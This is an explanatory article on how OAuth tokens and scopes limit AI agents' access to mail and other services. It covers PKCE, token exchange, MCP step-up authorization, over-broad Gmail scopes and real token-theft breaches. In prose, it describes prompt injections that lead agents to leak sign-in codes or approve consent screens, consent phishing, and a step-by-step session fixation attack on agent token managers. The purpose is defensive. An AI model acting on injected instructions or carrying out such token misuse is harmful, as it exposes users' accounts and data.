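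OpenAI's workplace test measured unintended outcomes that can happen without an attack, such as unauthorized purchases and disclosures of data, when instructions were ambiguous or several resources looked alike. The rate was 3.0% for GPT-6 Astra, down from 8.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol. Both models had instructions about when to ask the user for confirmation. OpenAI made the tasks deliberately difficult, so the rate in ordinary use is probably lower. A filter that looks for malicious text would not catch these mistakes, because they can begin with the user's own request.

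## How an OAuth token limits what an agent can do

When Alice connects her agent to her mail through OAuth, the application that runs the agent gets an access token tied to the permissions she approved. It never receives her password or session cookie. The mail service checks each request against those permissions, so if she hasn't approved sending, it can refuse to send a message even when a stranger's email has convinced the agent that she wants it sent.

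### From the consent screen to the token

OAuth divides the work among four parties. Alice is the resource owner, and the application is the client. An authorization server signs Alice in, asks for her consent and issues tokens. A resource server holds her mail and answers requests for it. Her mail provider would normally run both servers. The usual way for an application to get a token is the authorization code flow:

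1. The application generates a long random string, the code verifier, and keeps it secret. It computes a hash of the verifier, called the code challenge.
2. The application opens Alice's browser at the authorization server, with a request that contains the challenge and the scopes it wants.
3. Alice signs in if she hasn't already. The consent screen shows her the application's name and the permissions it wants, and she approves.
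4. The authorization server records the grant and sends her browser back to the application with a one-time code.
5. The application sends the code and the verifier directly to the authorization server, which hashes the verifier and compares the result with the challenge from step 2.
6. If the two match, the authorization server returns an access token and sometimes a refresh token, which the application can use to get more access tokens.
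7. The application calls the mail service with the access token in a header.
8. The mail service checks the token, then carries out the operation or refuses it.

The verifier and challenge make up PKCE (Proof Key for Code Exchange). The code passes through Alice's browser, where other software might intercept it. A thief who has only the code and the challenge cannot get a token, because nobody can feasibly work out the verifier from its hash.

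For the invoice task, the request in step 2 might look like this, split over several lines and without the encoding that web addresses need:

```
https://auth.mail.example/authorize
  ?response_type=code
  &client_id=assistant
  &redirect_uri=https://assistant.example/callback
  &scope=mail.search mail.read mail.draft
  &resource=https://api.mail.example
  &state=n7Qk2x
  &code_challenge=E9Melhoa2OwvFrEMTJguCHaoeK1t8URWbuGJSstw-cM
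  &code_challenge_method=S256
```

| Field | Meaning |
|---|---|
| response_type | The application wants a code, which it will trade for a token. |
| client_id | The application's identifier at the authorization server |
| redirect_uri | The address to which the browser returns with the code |
| scope | The permissions that the application wants |
| resource | The service where the application will use the token |
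| state | A random value that lets the application reject replies to requests it never made |
| code_challenge | The hash of the verifier |
| code_challenge_method | The method of hashing, here SHA-256 |

Many authorization servers issue the access token as a JSON Web Token, or JWT, a set of readable fields with the issuer's signature. Others issue a random string that the service looks up. The application can use either without understanding its contents, as Jones, Nadalin and colleagues explain in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (2020), an internet standard also known as RFC 8693. Decoded, Alice's token might contain these fields:

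```
{
  "iss": "https://auth.mail.example",
  "sub": "alice",
  "aud": "https://api.mail.example",
  "client_id": "assistant",
  "scope": "mail.search mail.read mail.draft",
  "iat": 1796464800,
  "exp": 1796465400,
  "jti": "a81f03c6"
}
```

| Field | Meaning |
|---|---|
| iss | The issuer, here the authorization server |
| sub | The subject, here Alice, whose account the token concerns |
| aud | The audience, meaning the service that should accept the token |
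| client_id | The application that requested the token |
| scope | The permissions that Alice granted |
| iat | The time of issue, in seconds since the start of 1970: 10:00 UTC on 5 December 2026 |
| exp | The expiry time, ten minutes later |
| jti | An identifier for this particular token |

When the agent saves a draft, the mail service verifies the token's signature and checks its issuer, audience and expiry time. It then checks that the token's scopes include mail.draft and saves the draft. If the agent tries to send the message with the same token, the service returns an error because the token lacks the scope for sending.

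Ordinary software can add the token to the request, so the model does not need access to it. Anthropic's *Federated cloud access* describes how a proxy does this for Claude Tag, the company's agent for Slack channels, from outside the agent's working environment. A malicious page therefore cannot get the model to reveal the token, but it can still get the model to make any call the token permits.

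### Scope and audience

A token's scopes limit which operations the agent can perform. Each service defines its own scopes, many of them broadly, and a token can be no narrower than those scopes allow. The three scopes in Alice's token are invented to fit her task, but they still cover her whole mailbox because an ordinary scope has no place for the accountant's address. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (2026) mentions an OAuth extension, Rich Authorization Requests, that can carry such details.

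A token's audience field limits which services accept it. Suppose the same authorization server issues tokens for Alice's mail service and for a small scheduling service. A dishonest scheduling service could present the token it receives from her agent to the mail service. The signature would be valid, but the mail service would reject the token because the audience field contains the scheduling service's address.

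A token with several audiences grants more access than it may appear to. Jones and colleagues explain that requesting several scopes at several services means requesting every scope at every service. If an agent needs to read mail and write to a calendar, one token with read and write scopes for both services would also let it write to the mailbox and read the calendar. A separate token for each service, with only the scope needed there, would avoid this.

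### Expiry, refresh and revocation

A short expiry time limits the damage from a leaked token. If Alice's token ends up in a log file, whoever finds it an hour later cannot use it. By comparison, Barth suggested that a session identifier expire after two weeks.

But the agent's access can last much longer than any one token, because an application with a refresh token can obtain new access tokens while Alice is asleep. *Position: AI Agents Need Authenticated Delegation* (South, Marro and colleagues, 2025) describes continued access in the user's absence as a key requirement behind OAuth. Continued access suits an agent that sorts mail every night. For a task involving one invoice, the authorization server could issue an access token without a refresh token, and the agent's access would end after ten minutes.

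Alice can also revoke the application's grant, usually from a page in her account settings. The authorization server then stops issuing tokens to that application, while her own session and her other applications continue to work. An access token that the application already holds will work until it expires if the mail service only verifies the token's signature and fields. A service that looks up every token can reject it immediately.

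Anthropic's documentation shows how these delays vary. When an administrator removes a connection to an authorization server, Claude stops using it within about a minute. An identity token already issued by Anthropic remains valid for up to ten minutes, and credentials already obtained from Amazon's cloud service remain valid for up to an hour. According to Anthropic's *Identity token reference*, nobody can revoke these tokens before they expire, but their short lifetime makes up for this.

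Revocation is harder to track when an application exchanges one token for another. Jones and colleagues treat the exchange as a one-time event, so revoking the original token does not generally revoke the new one.

### Proof of possession

Most access tokens are bearer tokens, which work for anyone who holds them (*Beyond OAuth*, 2026), as cookies do. OAuth has an optional remedy called Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP). *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) lists DPoP among the building blocks for agent credentials.

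With DPoP, the application creates a pair of cryptographic keys and keeps the private one. The authorization server puts a fingerprint of the public key in the token. For each call, the application signs a short statement containing the address, the HTTP method, the time and a hash of the token. The mail service checks that the signature was made with the key pair the fingerprint identifies. A thief who copies only the token cannot produce the signature.

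DPoP, like Device Bound Session Credentials, protects against credential theft but does not limit a misled agent, because the application still signs the agent's requests.

### What the agent may actually do

Alice's approval cannot give an agent more access than she has. Scopes limit what an application may do for a user, but they do not define the user's own rights, and the service holding the data makes the final decision, as Ibrahim and Li explain in *Overlaying Governance* (2026). The agent's effective permission is therefore the intersection of three sets, meaning only the operations that appear in all of them:

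```
effective permission = user's own rights ∩ granted scopes ∩ service's policy
```

Suppose Alice's mail service never lets outside applications change a recovery address or approve other applications. Its policy would then allow six of the eight operations in her account. The table shows how the rule applies to her invoice task and two variations.

| Case | Alice's own rights | Granted scopes | Service's policy | Effective permission |
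|---|---|---|---|---|
| Invoice task | All eight operations | Search, read, draft | Six operations | Search, read, draft |
| One scope for the whole account | All eight operations | All eight operations | Six operations | Search, read, draft, send, delete, set forwarding |
| Shared mailbox that Alice may only search and read | Search, read | Search, read, draft | Six operations | Search, read |

In the invoice task, most of the limits on the agent come from the scopes, which remove five operations, including the three whose effects would outlast the session. With the broad scope, only the service's policy protects Alice, and the agent can still set up forwarding. In the shared mailbox, granting the draft scope has no effect because Alice cannot create drafts there herself.

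The rule applies to messages as well as operations. Alice's token allows exactly the three operations the task requires, but if her mailbox holds 5,000 messages and only 12 are from the accountant, it also lets the agent read 4,988 messages it does not need. The token is still a large improvement on her session cookie.

### Delegation and impersonation

An access token can limit an agent without showing that an agent is involved. Jones and colleagues use the term "impersonation" for cases where the service cannot distinguish the acting party from the user, even if the token limits what that party can do or for how long. In delegation, the acting party keeps its own identity, and the service can see that it is acting for the user.

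Alice's token names her and the application, but thousands of agents may run on that application. McGuinness therefore separates the registered application, the person who authorized the access, and the agent using it. The difference would show in the mail service's log:

```
10:04:12  create draft  user=alice
10:04:12  create draft  user=alice  actor=agents/invoice-7
```

If Alice finds a draft she doesn't recognise, she can't tell from the first entry whether she or an agent wrote it. The second entry shows which agent wrote it, but not whether the agent was following her request or an instruction in somebody's email.

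Token exchange, the method that Jones and colleagues standardised, can produce a token that names both parties. The application sends the authorization server a subject token, which represents Alice, and an actor token, which represents the agent. The authorization server decides whether to allow the combination. If it does, it can issue a token with Alice as the subject and the agent in a field called act:

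```
"sub": "alice",
"scope": "mail.search mail.read mail.draft",
"act": { "sub": "https://assistant.example/agents/invoice-7" }
```

If the application sends only the subject token, the result can only be impersonation.

The standard also covers chains of agents. If Alice's agent passes the invoice to a second agent that extracts the amounts, another token exchange can put the second agent in the act field, with the first nested inside it. When deciding on access, the service may consider the current actor but must ignore the earlier ones, which are recorded only as history.

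Each agent in a chain should receive no more access than the one before it, but token exchange does not guarantee this. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) points out that an application can request and receive scopes that an earlier agent in the chain did not have. A well-configured authorization server would refuse such a request, but the standard leaves the decision to the server's policy. Otsuka and colleagues say there is still no deployed standard for verifying a chain of delegations.

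### Credentials for the agent itself

In a position paper presented at the 2025 International Conference on Machine Learning, South and colleagues propose giving agents their own credentials. They criticise OpenAI's Operator, an early browser agent, for storing logins as cookies, which made it harder for users to limit the agent's permissions, revoke its access or review what it had done. They also describe an agent that signs in to a medical portal with a doctor's ordinary credentials. The portal treats the agent as if it could do everything the doctor can, including watch a video with a specialist's spoken comments. The agent can read only text, so it misses the comments and gives an incomplete diagnosis.

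Their design uses three tokens:

- **User ID token.** This is the token that existing sign-in systems already issue to identify a person.
- **Agent ID token.** This identifies the agent and can describe its capabilities and limitations.
- **Delegation token.** The user signs this token, which refers to the other two and states what the agent may do and until when. It can also include a summary of the goal and an address for revoking the delegation.

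In the medical example, the agent's token could include the text-only limitation, and the portal could then prompt a person to review the video.

South and colleagues want enforceable permissions rather than a prompt that tells the agent what to avoid. Under their proposal, a user would describe the limits in ordinary language, a model would translate them into formal rules, and the user would check the rules before they took effect. They acknowledge that the model might translate badly, and they leave testing of that step to future work. They also discuss objections that the system would add friction, overburden small developers, and give large identity providers more power and more data about users. They reply that an imperfect system would still improve security and could be refined later. That reply is reasonable for the identity and delegation tokens, which extend widely used methods.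 It is less certain for the translation step, because a user who finds formal rules hard to write may also find them hard to check.

### The Workload Authorization Grant

Companies have a further problem because many of their agents work for a team rather than one person. Otsuka and colleagues cite a figure that 45.6% of organisations run agents on shared API keys, which are long-lived secrets that identify a program to a service. If ten agents share a key, the service cannot tell them apart, and cutting off one agent means replacing the key for all ten.

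In December 2026, Anthropic's *Workload Authorization Grant* (2026) announced a trial of a method that gives each agent a separate identity. Pogorelec (2026), in *Anthropic tests giving Claude agents their own credentials*, reports that the trial is a public beta in Claude Tag, whereas teams must request access to it in Claude Managed Agents. The specification, *Workload Authorization Grant* (Carleton, Steele and colleagues, 2026), has editors from Anthropic, OpenAI, Okta, Defakto Security and Ping Identity. It works in three steps:

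1. An administrator configures a service's authorization server, once, to trust the platform that runs the agents.
2. The platform creates an agent and gives it a permanent identifier. It doesn't need to notify the service.
3. When the agent needs access, the platform signs a short-lived grant with the agent's identifier in it. The agent presents the grant to the authorization server, which returns an access token.

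The service decides what each agent may do. In an example by Carleton and colleagues, an agent has a role called "databases-team". A ticket tracker lets that role read tickets and write comments, which is less than the team's human members can do. A log service gives the role the same access as the team. The platform can ask for particular scopes, and the authorization server may grant only some of them. The server must not issue refresh tokens, so the agent has to present a new grant when its access token expires.

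The method does not yet cover Alice's task because it deals only with agents acting on their own behalf. Carleton and colleagues leave access on behalf of a user to other standards, such as token exchange. They describe the document as an early, exploratory draft, and it has no formal standing at the IETF, the body that publishes internet standards. They have also not decided whether to require proof of possession. Without that proof, someone who stole a grant could use it until it expired.

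Anthropic's identity tokens for Claude Tag include the organization and the agent, and can include the Slack channel, but they contain no information about the person who made the request. A service could log that the engineering channel's agent deleted a file but have no record of which engineer asked it to.

The user's rights may not limit the agent either. Anthropic's *Agent identity in Claude Tag* explains that someone who cannot open a code repository can ask Claude to read it, if the channel's profile gives Claude access. The agent's rights replace the user's in the intersection rule. This is convenient for a team, but everyone in the channel gains the agent's access, so an administrator has to set that access with the least trusted member in mind. Curity's *AI Agent Access Control* argues that Anthropic's model encourages broad, persistent permissions. Curity sells competing authorization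 software, but the concern is fair where a channel has many members or its agent can reach sensitive data.

A receiving service can also mistakenly accept a token from another company's agent. All Claude Tag organizations share one issuer, so such a token can have a genuine signature, the expected issuer and a valid expiry time. For some destinations, such as Amazon's cloud, the audience is also the same. Anthropic therefore tells services to check the organization in the subject field, and warns that standard libraries do not do this. *Connect an authorization server* adds that Anthropic's console does not test this check for authorization servers, so administrators must confirm it themselves.

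### The Model Context Protocol

Anthropic introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP) in 2024 as a standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data. An MCP server might let an agent search mail or create a draft. In OAuth terms, the MCP server is the resource server and the agent's application is the client. WorkOS's *What is MCP authorization?* (2026) describes the protocol's 28 July 2026 revision as current in September.

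The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) makes authorization optional, but says that web-based servers that support it should use the protocol's OAuth procedure. Programs that communicate with a server on the same computer should instead get credentials from their local environment.

An application that connects to Alice's mail over the web first sends a request without a token. The MCP server rejects the request and returns the location of the authorization server's details. The response should also list the scopes the request needs. The application then goes through the authorization code flow with PKCE. It must specify the MCP server in the resource field, and that server must reject tokens issued for any other service.

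Applications should request only the scopes they need. If the server refuses a request without listing the scopes required, the application requests every scope in the server's published list of supported scopes. Under the specification, that list is meant to contain only the minimum for basic use, so a developer who publishes every available scope could lead applications to request more access than they need.

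An agent can ask for more access during a task. If Alice's agent tries to send a message, the server can refuse and identify the missing scope:

```
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope", scope="mail.send"
```

The application adds mail.send to its three earlier scopes and starts authorization again. If Alice approves, the application receives a new token and retries the request. The protocol's term for this is step-up authorization. The Agentic AI Foundation explains that long tasks may need additional privileges as new information emerges. Alice can therefore start with narrow permissions and decide whether to allow sending only if the application needs it.

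This suits agents, but a prompt injection may trigger the request for more access. Alice might approve the request because she wants the task to finish, or a browser agent might approve it for her, as Hossen's agents did.

Step-up authorization also tends to accumulate permissions, because the application should include its earlier scopes in each new request to avoid losing access it still needs. If Alice approves mail.send for one message, the new token permits sending other messages too. WorkOS's *MCP: Scope step-up is not authentication step-up* describes an agent that calls an operation to delete a production database, using a scope the user granted three hours earlier. The token is valid and the scope is sufficient, so the request proceeds. MCP has no standard way for the server to require confirmation that the user is still there.

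An employee may never see a consent screen. Anthropic offers a beta feature called Enterprise Managed Auth, in which the employer's identity provider confirms the employee's identity and the MCP server's authorization server issues a token without asking the employee for consent. Administrators can then set the limits centrally, but narrow access still depends on what the application requests. According to documentation from C1, an identity provider, its system grants the requested scopes that the service enables and the user holds. If the application requests no particular scopes, C1 grants all the enabled scopes that the user holds. C1 says most applications that connect this way request no particular scopes, and gives Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, as an example.

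### Cookies and tokens compared

The differences between cookies and tokens in the table come from how services usually use them. A service can define a single scope for the whole account, and a token with that scope would give an agent about as much access as a cookie. A website can also store a list of allowed operations in a session record, and a cookie pointing to that record would be as limited as Alice's token.

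| | Session cookie | OAuth access token |
|---|---|---|
| What it permits | Everything the signed-in user may do | Operations within the granted scopes, the user's own rights and the service's policy |
| Who chooses the permissions | The website, which normally gives every session the user's full rights | The application requests scopes, and the user or an administrator approves them |
| Where it is valid | The website that set it, sometimes including subdomains | The service in its audience field |
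| How long it lasts | Often days or weeks | Often minutes or hours, though a refresh token can extend the access |
| Separate revocation | Only if the agent has its own session | Yes, by revoking the application's grant, though an issued token may work until it expires |
| Attribution in logs | The user | The user and the application, and also the agent if the token names it |

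## Where OAuth scopes grant too much

Gmail's published scopes are broader than the invented ones in Alice's mail.example token. If she uses Gmail, her agent gets more access than the task needs, even if its developer asks for as little as possible.

### Alice's task in Gmail

Google lists 14 scopes for Gmail, four of which let an application write drafts: gmail.compose, gmail.modify, the full-access scope mail.google.com, and a scope for add-ons that run inside Gmail. All four also allow sending, so Alice cannot let an application draft a reply without letting it send one. Claude's Gmail connector would need permission to send even if it only wrote drafts.

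No Gmail scope limits reading to one sender. The gmail.readonly scope lets an agent read every message in the mailbox, as well as the mail settings. A narrower scope, gmail.metadata, hides the body of each message, so an agent looking for an accountant's invoice could see that the accountant had written but could not read the invoice.

For an ordinary outside application, the smallest grant that covers the task appears to be gmail.readonly plus gmail.compose. The gmail.modify scope would cover the task by itself, but it would also let the agent move messages to the trash.

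| Operation | What the task needs | What the smallest Gmail grant allows |
|---|---|---|
| Search | The accountant's messages | The whole mailbox |
| Read | The accountant's messages | The whole mailbox and the mail settings |
| Draft | A reply to the accountant | Drafts to anyone, and changes to existing drafts |
| Send | Nothing | Messages to anyone |
| Delete | Nothing | Drafts only |
| Set forwarding | Nothing | Nothing |
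| Change recovery address | Nothing | Nothing |
| Approve third-party applications | Nothing | Nothing |

This is still much safer than a session cookie, because the agent cannot set up forwarding, change the recovery address or approve other applications. The main danger is that the agent can read the whole mailbox and send email to anyone. A stranger could write an email that tricks the agent into finding a sign-in code elsewhere in the mailbox and sending it out. If the agent could only write drafts, the message would not go out unless Alice sent it.

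Alice can avoid this by approving only gmail.readonly and having the agent write its reply in the chat for her to copy. This takes her an extra minute. The agent then can't send email, but it can still read her whole mailbox.

Google's *Restricted scope verification* tells developers not to request full mailbox access for an application that only sends occasional mail. Google's *Restricted Scopes* places both gmail.readonly and gmail.compose in the class with the strictest review. But Gmail has no draft-only scope, so an application that only writes drafts must still request broader access.

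The classes also reflect how much data an application can see more than they reflect what it can do. The gmail.send scope is in a less strict class than gmail.compose, so an application that only sends mail in Alice's name gets a lighter review than one that also manages her drafts.

### When no grant is the smallest

Least privilege requires a way to tell which of two grants is smaller. Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, examined how often this is possible, using Microsoft's and Google's tables of the scopes that authorise each operation. The Microsoft tables cover Graph, the programming interface to Microsoft 365 data such as mail, files and calendars.

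Xu compares grants by the operations they allow:

```
M(s) = the operations that scope s allows
A(F) = the operations that the scopes in grant F allow together

F is sufficient for task T      if T ⊆ A(F)
F is no larger than grant G     if A(F) ⊆ A(G)
```

For example, mail.google.com allows everything gmail.compose allows and more, so gmail.compose is smaller. But gmail.send and gmail.readonly can't be ranked this way, because each allows something the other doesn't.

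A sufficient grant is minimal if no other sufficient grant allows only part of what it allows. Some tasks have two or more minimal grants that allow different operations, so no single grant is the smallest. Xu found this in 29.8% of 493 Graph tasks for applications acting for a user with a work account, 30.7% of 450 tasks for applications acting on their own, and 33.3% of only 24 tasks for personal accounts. The figure was 3.2% for 2,822 Google tasks, each made up of the operations on one type of resource. Xu links the lower figure to Google's finer scopes within each service.

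One of the Google tasks is to read project metadata in BigQuery, a service for analysing large datasets. Two scopes are minimal for it:

| | bigquery | cloud-platform.read-only |
|---|---|---|
| Operations allowed | 286 | 565 |
| Operations that change something | 144 | 61 |
| Services reached | 10 | 27 |

The cloud-platform.read-only scope looks safer if the owner mostly fears that an agent will damage data, although by Xu's count even this scope allows some changes. For an owner more worried about leaks, bigquery is probably better because it reaches fewer services. Google could remove the need to choose by adding a scope that allows only the operations the two share, which are enough for the whole task.

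Microsoft gives almost every Graph permission a privilege level from 1 to 4, but the levels often don't help in choosing between minimal permissions for the same task. The competing permissions have the same level in 67.4% of pairs for work accounts and 74.4% of pairs for applications acting on their own. For a task that involves listing and creating OAuth grants, one minimal permission gives access to 355 endpoints (addresses for particular operations) and another to 11, yet Microsoft puts both at level 4. The scale is coarse in general, since the levels are also the same in about 61% of the pairs where one grant clearly contains the other.

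A task without a single smallest grant in Xu's sense may still have an obvious best choice, such as a grant covering 11 endpoints over one covering 355. Xu also compared grants by how many operations they allow, how many of those operations change something, how many services they reach, and whether they reach administrative functions. For 28.7% of competing Google pairs and 15.7% to 23.4% of those in the two main Graph groups, two of these measures ranked the grants in opposite orders, so someone has to decide which risk matters more.

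### How models choose between grants

Xu asked six frontier models, each from a different vendor, to choose among grants that were all sufficient for a task. In one experiment, every option was minimal. The models first saw only the permission names, then also saw the number of operations each grant allowed. In another experiment, Xu mixed minimal grants with larger ones and told the models to choose the grant that gave the least additional authority.

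| Options | Decisions | Chose the fewest operations | Chose a grant that another option matched or beat on all four counts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Minimal grants, names only | 588 | 54.6% | 32.3% |
| Minimal grants, with the number of operations | 588 | 79.9% | 12.9% |
| Minimal and larger grants mixed | 1,708 | 74.1% | 22.1% |

In the mixed experiment, the models chose a minimal grant 99.0% of the time, so they would score nearly full marks on a benchmark that checked only for minimal grants. Yet 18.1% of their choices allowed at least twice as many operations as the narrowest option. The numbers helped some models far more than others. With them, three models chose the narrowest grant at least 95.9% of the time, while the other three did so between 53.1% and 76.5% of the time.

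Software can compute these counts from the published tables, so a developer has little reason to let a model guess from names. Xu recommends showing the alternatives to whoever approves the grant, which makes sense when the counts conflict.

The study's main limit is that Xu generated the tasks from the tables by grouping related operations, so the roughly 30% figure for Graph is not the share of real errands that lack a smallest grant. The models also chose from a fixed list, whereas a deployed agent's software has to write its own request and might request too little or name a scope that doesn't exist.

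Xu's results are more encouraging about asking for permissions one step at a time, as the Model Context Protocol allows. In 23,448 simulated Google workflows, taking the narrowest option at each step produced the smallest grant for the whole workflow at least 98.8% of the time. But the smallest available grant can still be too large, as Alice's Gmail task shows.

### Why applications ask for more than they need

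Sometimes a service offers no scope as narrow as the developer needs. *OAuthHub* (Li, Tian and Jin, 2026) gives the example of a feature that collects travel itineraries from flight confirmations. The feature has to request access to all of the user's email because Gmail has no scope for confirmations alone.

Li and colleagues installed 62 applications from Google's Workspace marketplace and compared the access each requested with what it seemed to need. They judged that 50 of them (81%) asked for too much. Many requested permission to read and change everything of a given type, such as all the files in Google Drive, when they needed only certain folders or file types. Two of the researchers used the applications' descriptions to infer what access each one needed, so the figure is approximate. It also doesn't distinguish developers who had no narrower scope available from those who ignored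 one.

Developers may also request too many permissions for agents because they can't predict what users will ask the agents to do. A calendar application with three features can request only the permissions those features need. But the developer of an MCP server may request every permission that any future task could require, as Vargas, Bouhmad and Rodríguez explain in *From all-or-nothing to task-based OAuth consent*. The user may want the agent only to check an order, yet the consent screen may also include permission to issue refunds.

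Many services then bundle the permissions into one decision, so the user must approve everything or go without the application. InfoQ's *Cloudflare Adds Optional OAuth Scopes, Letting Developers Mark What Users May Decline* cites the software engineer Umesh Malik, who says that requesting few permissions breaks advanced features, while requesting many drives users away. If developers request many anyway, the users who accept bear the risk of the extra access.

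Convenience is another reason products request broad scopes, since one connection can then serve every feature. In *How to set Gmail OAuth for ONLY READ?*, a thread on the forum of the automation tool n8n, a user had set up read-only scopes, but according to a reply, n8n's built-in Gmail connection added gmail.modify and gmail.compose to the request. If the user declined them, the connection failed with an error. The suggested solution was to build a custom connection, which most people would not do for a single task.

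Developers may not use narrow permissions even when a service offers them. Longo, Verna and colleagues (2026), in *Lost in Permissions*, collected data on more than 8,000 Microsoft 365 applications but could get both a description and a list of permissions for only 1,069. They grouped these by purpose and looked for unusual permissions with three detection methods. All three flagged the same 139 applications (13%).

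Longo and colleagues examined eight of the flagged applications by hand and concluded that six seemed to have excessive permissions, although their individual descriptions clearly support this for only four. One, a holiday tracker, could change the calendar of everyone in the organisation. Another, for booking desks, could delete any chat message. The researchers looked only at what access the applications requested, not at how they used it.

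Some of these were application permissions, which Microsoft grants to the software itself, so the user's rights don't limit them. The holiday tracker could change calendars that the employee using it couldn't open. Microsoft also offers permissions for a single team or chat, but few applications in the sample used them. The detection methods flagged two applications as unusual largely because they used these permissions.

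Excessive OAuth requests predate AI agents. *Exploring Privacy Implications in OAuth Deployments* (Morkonda, van Oorschot and Chiasson, 2021) studied login buttons on the 500 most visited sites in each of five countries. It found that the same site would request different amounts of personal data depending on whether the user signed in through Google, Facebook, Apple or LinkedIn. If a site works for users who share less through Apple, it probably doesn't need everything it requests through Facebook.

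### Optional scopes

In September 2026, Cloudflare, which provides network services for websites, started letting users decline some of the access an application requests. The developer marks each scope as required or optional, and the user can deselect the optional ones on the consent screen. Cloudflare then issues a token with only the scopes the user approved.

In an example from Vargas and colleagues, an application requests four scopes. It needs to read the user's details and write scripts, but it can work without writing to storage or reading website settings. If the user deselects storage, the application receives the other three scopes. It must check which scopes it received and turn off any feature that needs the missing one. If the application later requests only two of the four, the consent screen shows only those two.

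The OAuth standard already allowed a service to grant less than an application requested, as InfoQ points out, and GitHub and Google already let users narrow some requests. Cloudflare adds a way for the developer to indicate which permissions the application can do without. This should prevent failures like the one in the n8n thread, where the connection stopped working after the user declined a permission.

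Optional scopes are a modest remedy. A developer can still mark every scope as required, and users grant the full request unless they change it on the consent screen. Optional scopes also can't separate permissions that the service has combined into one scope. Because gmail.compose covers both drafting and sending, Alice could refuse the whole scope but couldn't allow only drafting.

Developers may have a reason to request narrower permissions, though. When Li and colleagues showed permission requests to 100 participants, people were 56% to 78% less likely to refuse the narrower versions. Those versions relied on software on the user's device that filters data before passing it on. The original service doesn't need to add scopes, but the filtering software itself needs broad access, and each application has to support it.

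### When an attacker obtains a grant

Excess permissions do little harm if an honest application leaves them unused, but they can do much more if an attacker controls the application or its tokens. Microsoft's *Defending SaaS based applications against ShinyHunters OAuth abuse* (2026) describes a year of such attacks on companies that store customer records with Salesforce.

In the attacks that began in mid-2025, callers posed as IT support and talked employees through a consent screen. The screen asked them to approve the attackers' application, which looked like Data Loader, a genuine Salesforce tool. This is consent phishing, in which an attacker tricks someone into granting access rather than revealing a password. A second login factor doesn't prevent it, because the real user signs in to the real service. Once the employee approved, the application could use that employee's permissions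 to copy records. An attacker wouldn't need to phone anyone if a browser agent approved the consent screen, as Hossen's agents did.

Attackers can also steal tokens from a legitimate application that many companies have approved. The best-documented case involved Drift, Salesloft's AI chat agent for sales teams. *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues, 2025) reports that an attacker used stolen Drift tokens to export data from Drift customers' Salesforce accounts from at least 8 to 18 August 2025. Larsen told CyberScoop that Google knew of more than 700 potentially affected organisations.

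The attacker first counted the records in each account, then downloaded user details and support cases. The attacker then searched the stolen data for passwords and for access keys to other cloud services. Read access to one service could therefore lead to much broader access elsewhere. The attacker also used tokens from Drift's email integration to read mail in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts.

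On 20 August, Salesloft and Salesforce revoked all of Drift's access and refresh tokens. Short-lived access tokens would have given limited protection if the attacker also had the refresh tokens. Narrower permissions would probably have helped more, because a sales chat tool has little obvious need to export thousands of support cases at once.

Similar thefts followed through applications from Gainsight in November 2025 and the market intelligence platform Klue in June 2026, according to Microsoft. *Klue Breach Enables Hackers to Compromise Cybersecurity Firms* (Poireault, 2026) reports that at least five cybersecurity firms confirmed the Klue breach had affected them. The hosting company Vercel traced another breach to a small AI tool with access to an employee's Google account. Vercel said the compromise of the tool's OAuth application may have affected hundreds of users across many organisations,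 according to Help Net Security's *Vercel breached via compromised third-party AI tool*.

These attacks are hard to spot because the tokens are genuine and the requests resemble the application's normal work. Microsoft found that the thefts often produced no unusual sign-ins. A narrow token would make some misuse easier to notice, because the service would start refusing requests that the application had never made.

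Old grants add to the exposure. Microsoft says organisations often connect an application for temporary use and rarely remove it, so it keeps its permissions. Li and colleagues found that most OAuth providers end an application's access only after six months without use, and a few never do. Of the 62 applications they studied, 43 needed data only during setup or while the user was actively using them, so access at other times added risk without benefiting the user. Alice should revoke her agent's grant once she has the invoice, unless she expects to use it again soon.

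### Services that hold tokens for agents

Drift held tokens for many customers, which made it a valuable target. Some agent platforms now offer to hold tokens for many agents. Developers then don't have to build the OAuth process or secure the tokens themselves, but this also creates new ways to connect people to the wrong accounts.

Luo, Wang and colleagues examined these services in *Back to the Future*, a talk at the 2025 Black Hat security conference. The platform runs a token manager, which stores the tokens and gives each agent a connection identifier. Each connection links one user, one agent and one tool, such as Alice, her invoice agent and Gmail. To get her mail, the agent presents the connection identifier and a key that identifies the agent's developer. The token manager then either returns the token or makes the request itself.

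OAuth normally treats the application as a single party. Here the application is split between the agent, which knows which user started the process, and the token manager, which receives the token. The OAuth standards don't cover this split, so each platform has designed its own way to handle it. Luo and colleagues found that several of these designs allowed attacks that the standards had already addressed.

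One of these is session fixation. Suppose Mallory uses the same agent as Alice and wants her mail:

1. Mallory asks the agent to connect a Gmail account. The token manager creates a connection in Mallory's name and returns a link to Google's authorization page.
2. Mallory sends the link to Alice instead of opening it.
3. Alice opens it while signed in to Google. She approves the request because she recognises the agent, or Google may not ask again if she has approved it before.
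4. The token manager receives a token for Alice's mailbox and stores it under Mallory's connection.
5. Mallory asks the agent to search the connected mailbox, and it searches Alice's.

In ordinary OAuth, the application prevents this by using the state value to check that the same browser starts and finishes the process. A token manager that checks only whether the state value matches a connection won't detect a change of browser, because the value does match Mallory's connection. The platform has to apply the browser check across both halves of the process.

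Luo and colleagues also describe attacks in which a malicious agent targets another agent on the same platform, or a malicious tool targets another tool. In some cases the attacker could take over the user's account at the connected service without the user's explicit consent. Their 2024 study had already found related flaws in 24 major platforms, including voice assistants, smart home systems and services that connected language models to outside tools. The flaws come from linking a token to the wrong party. Narrower scopes would not prevent this, but they would limit what Mallory could do with Alice's mailbox.

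## Permissions that fit a single task

An OAuth scope names an operation but usually doesn't include the values the agent may use with it. For example, if Alice asks an agent to transfer $100 to Bob, a scope can allow the agent to make transfers but doesn't specify the amount or the recipient, so the agent could use the same token to send $5,000 to a stranger.

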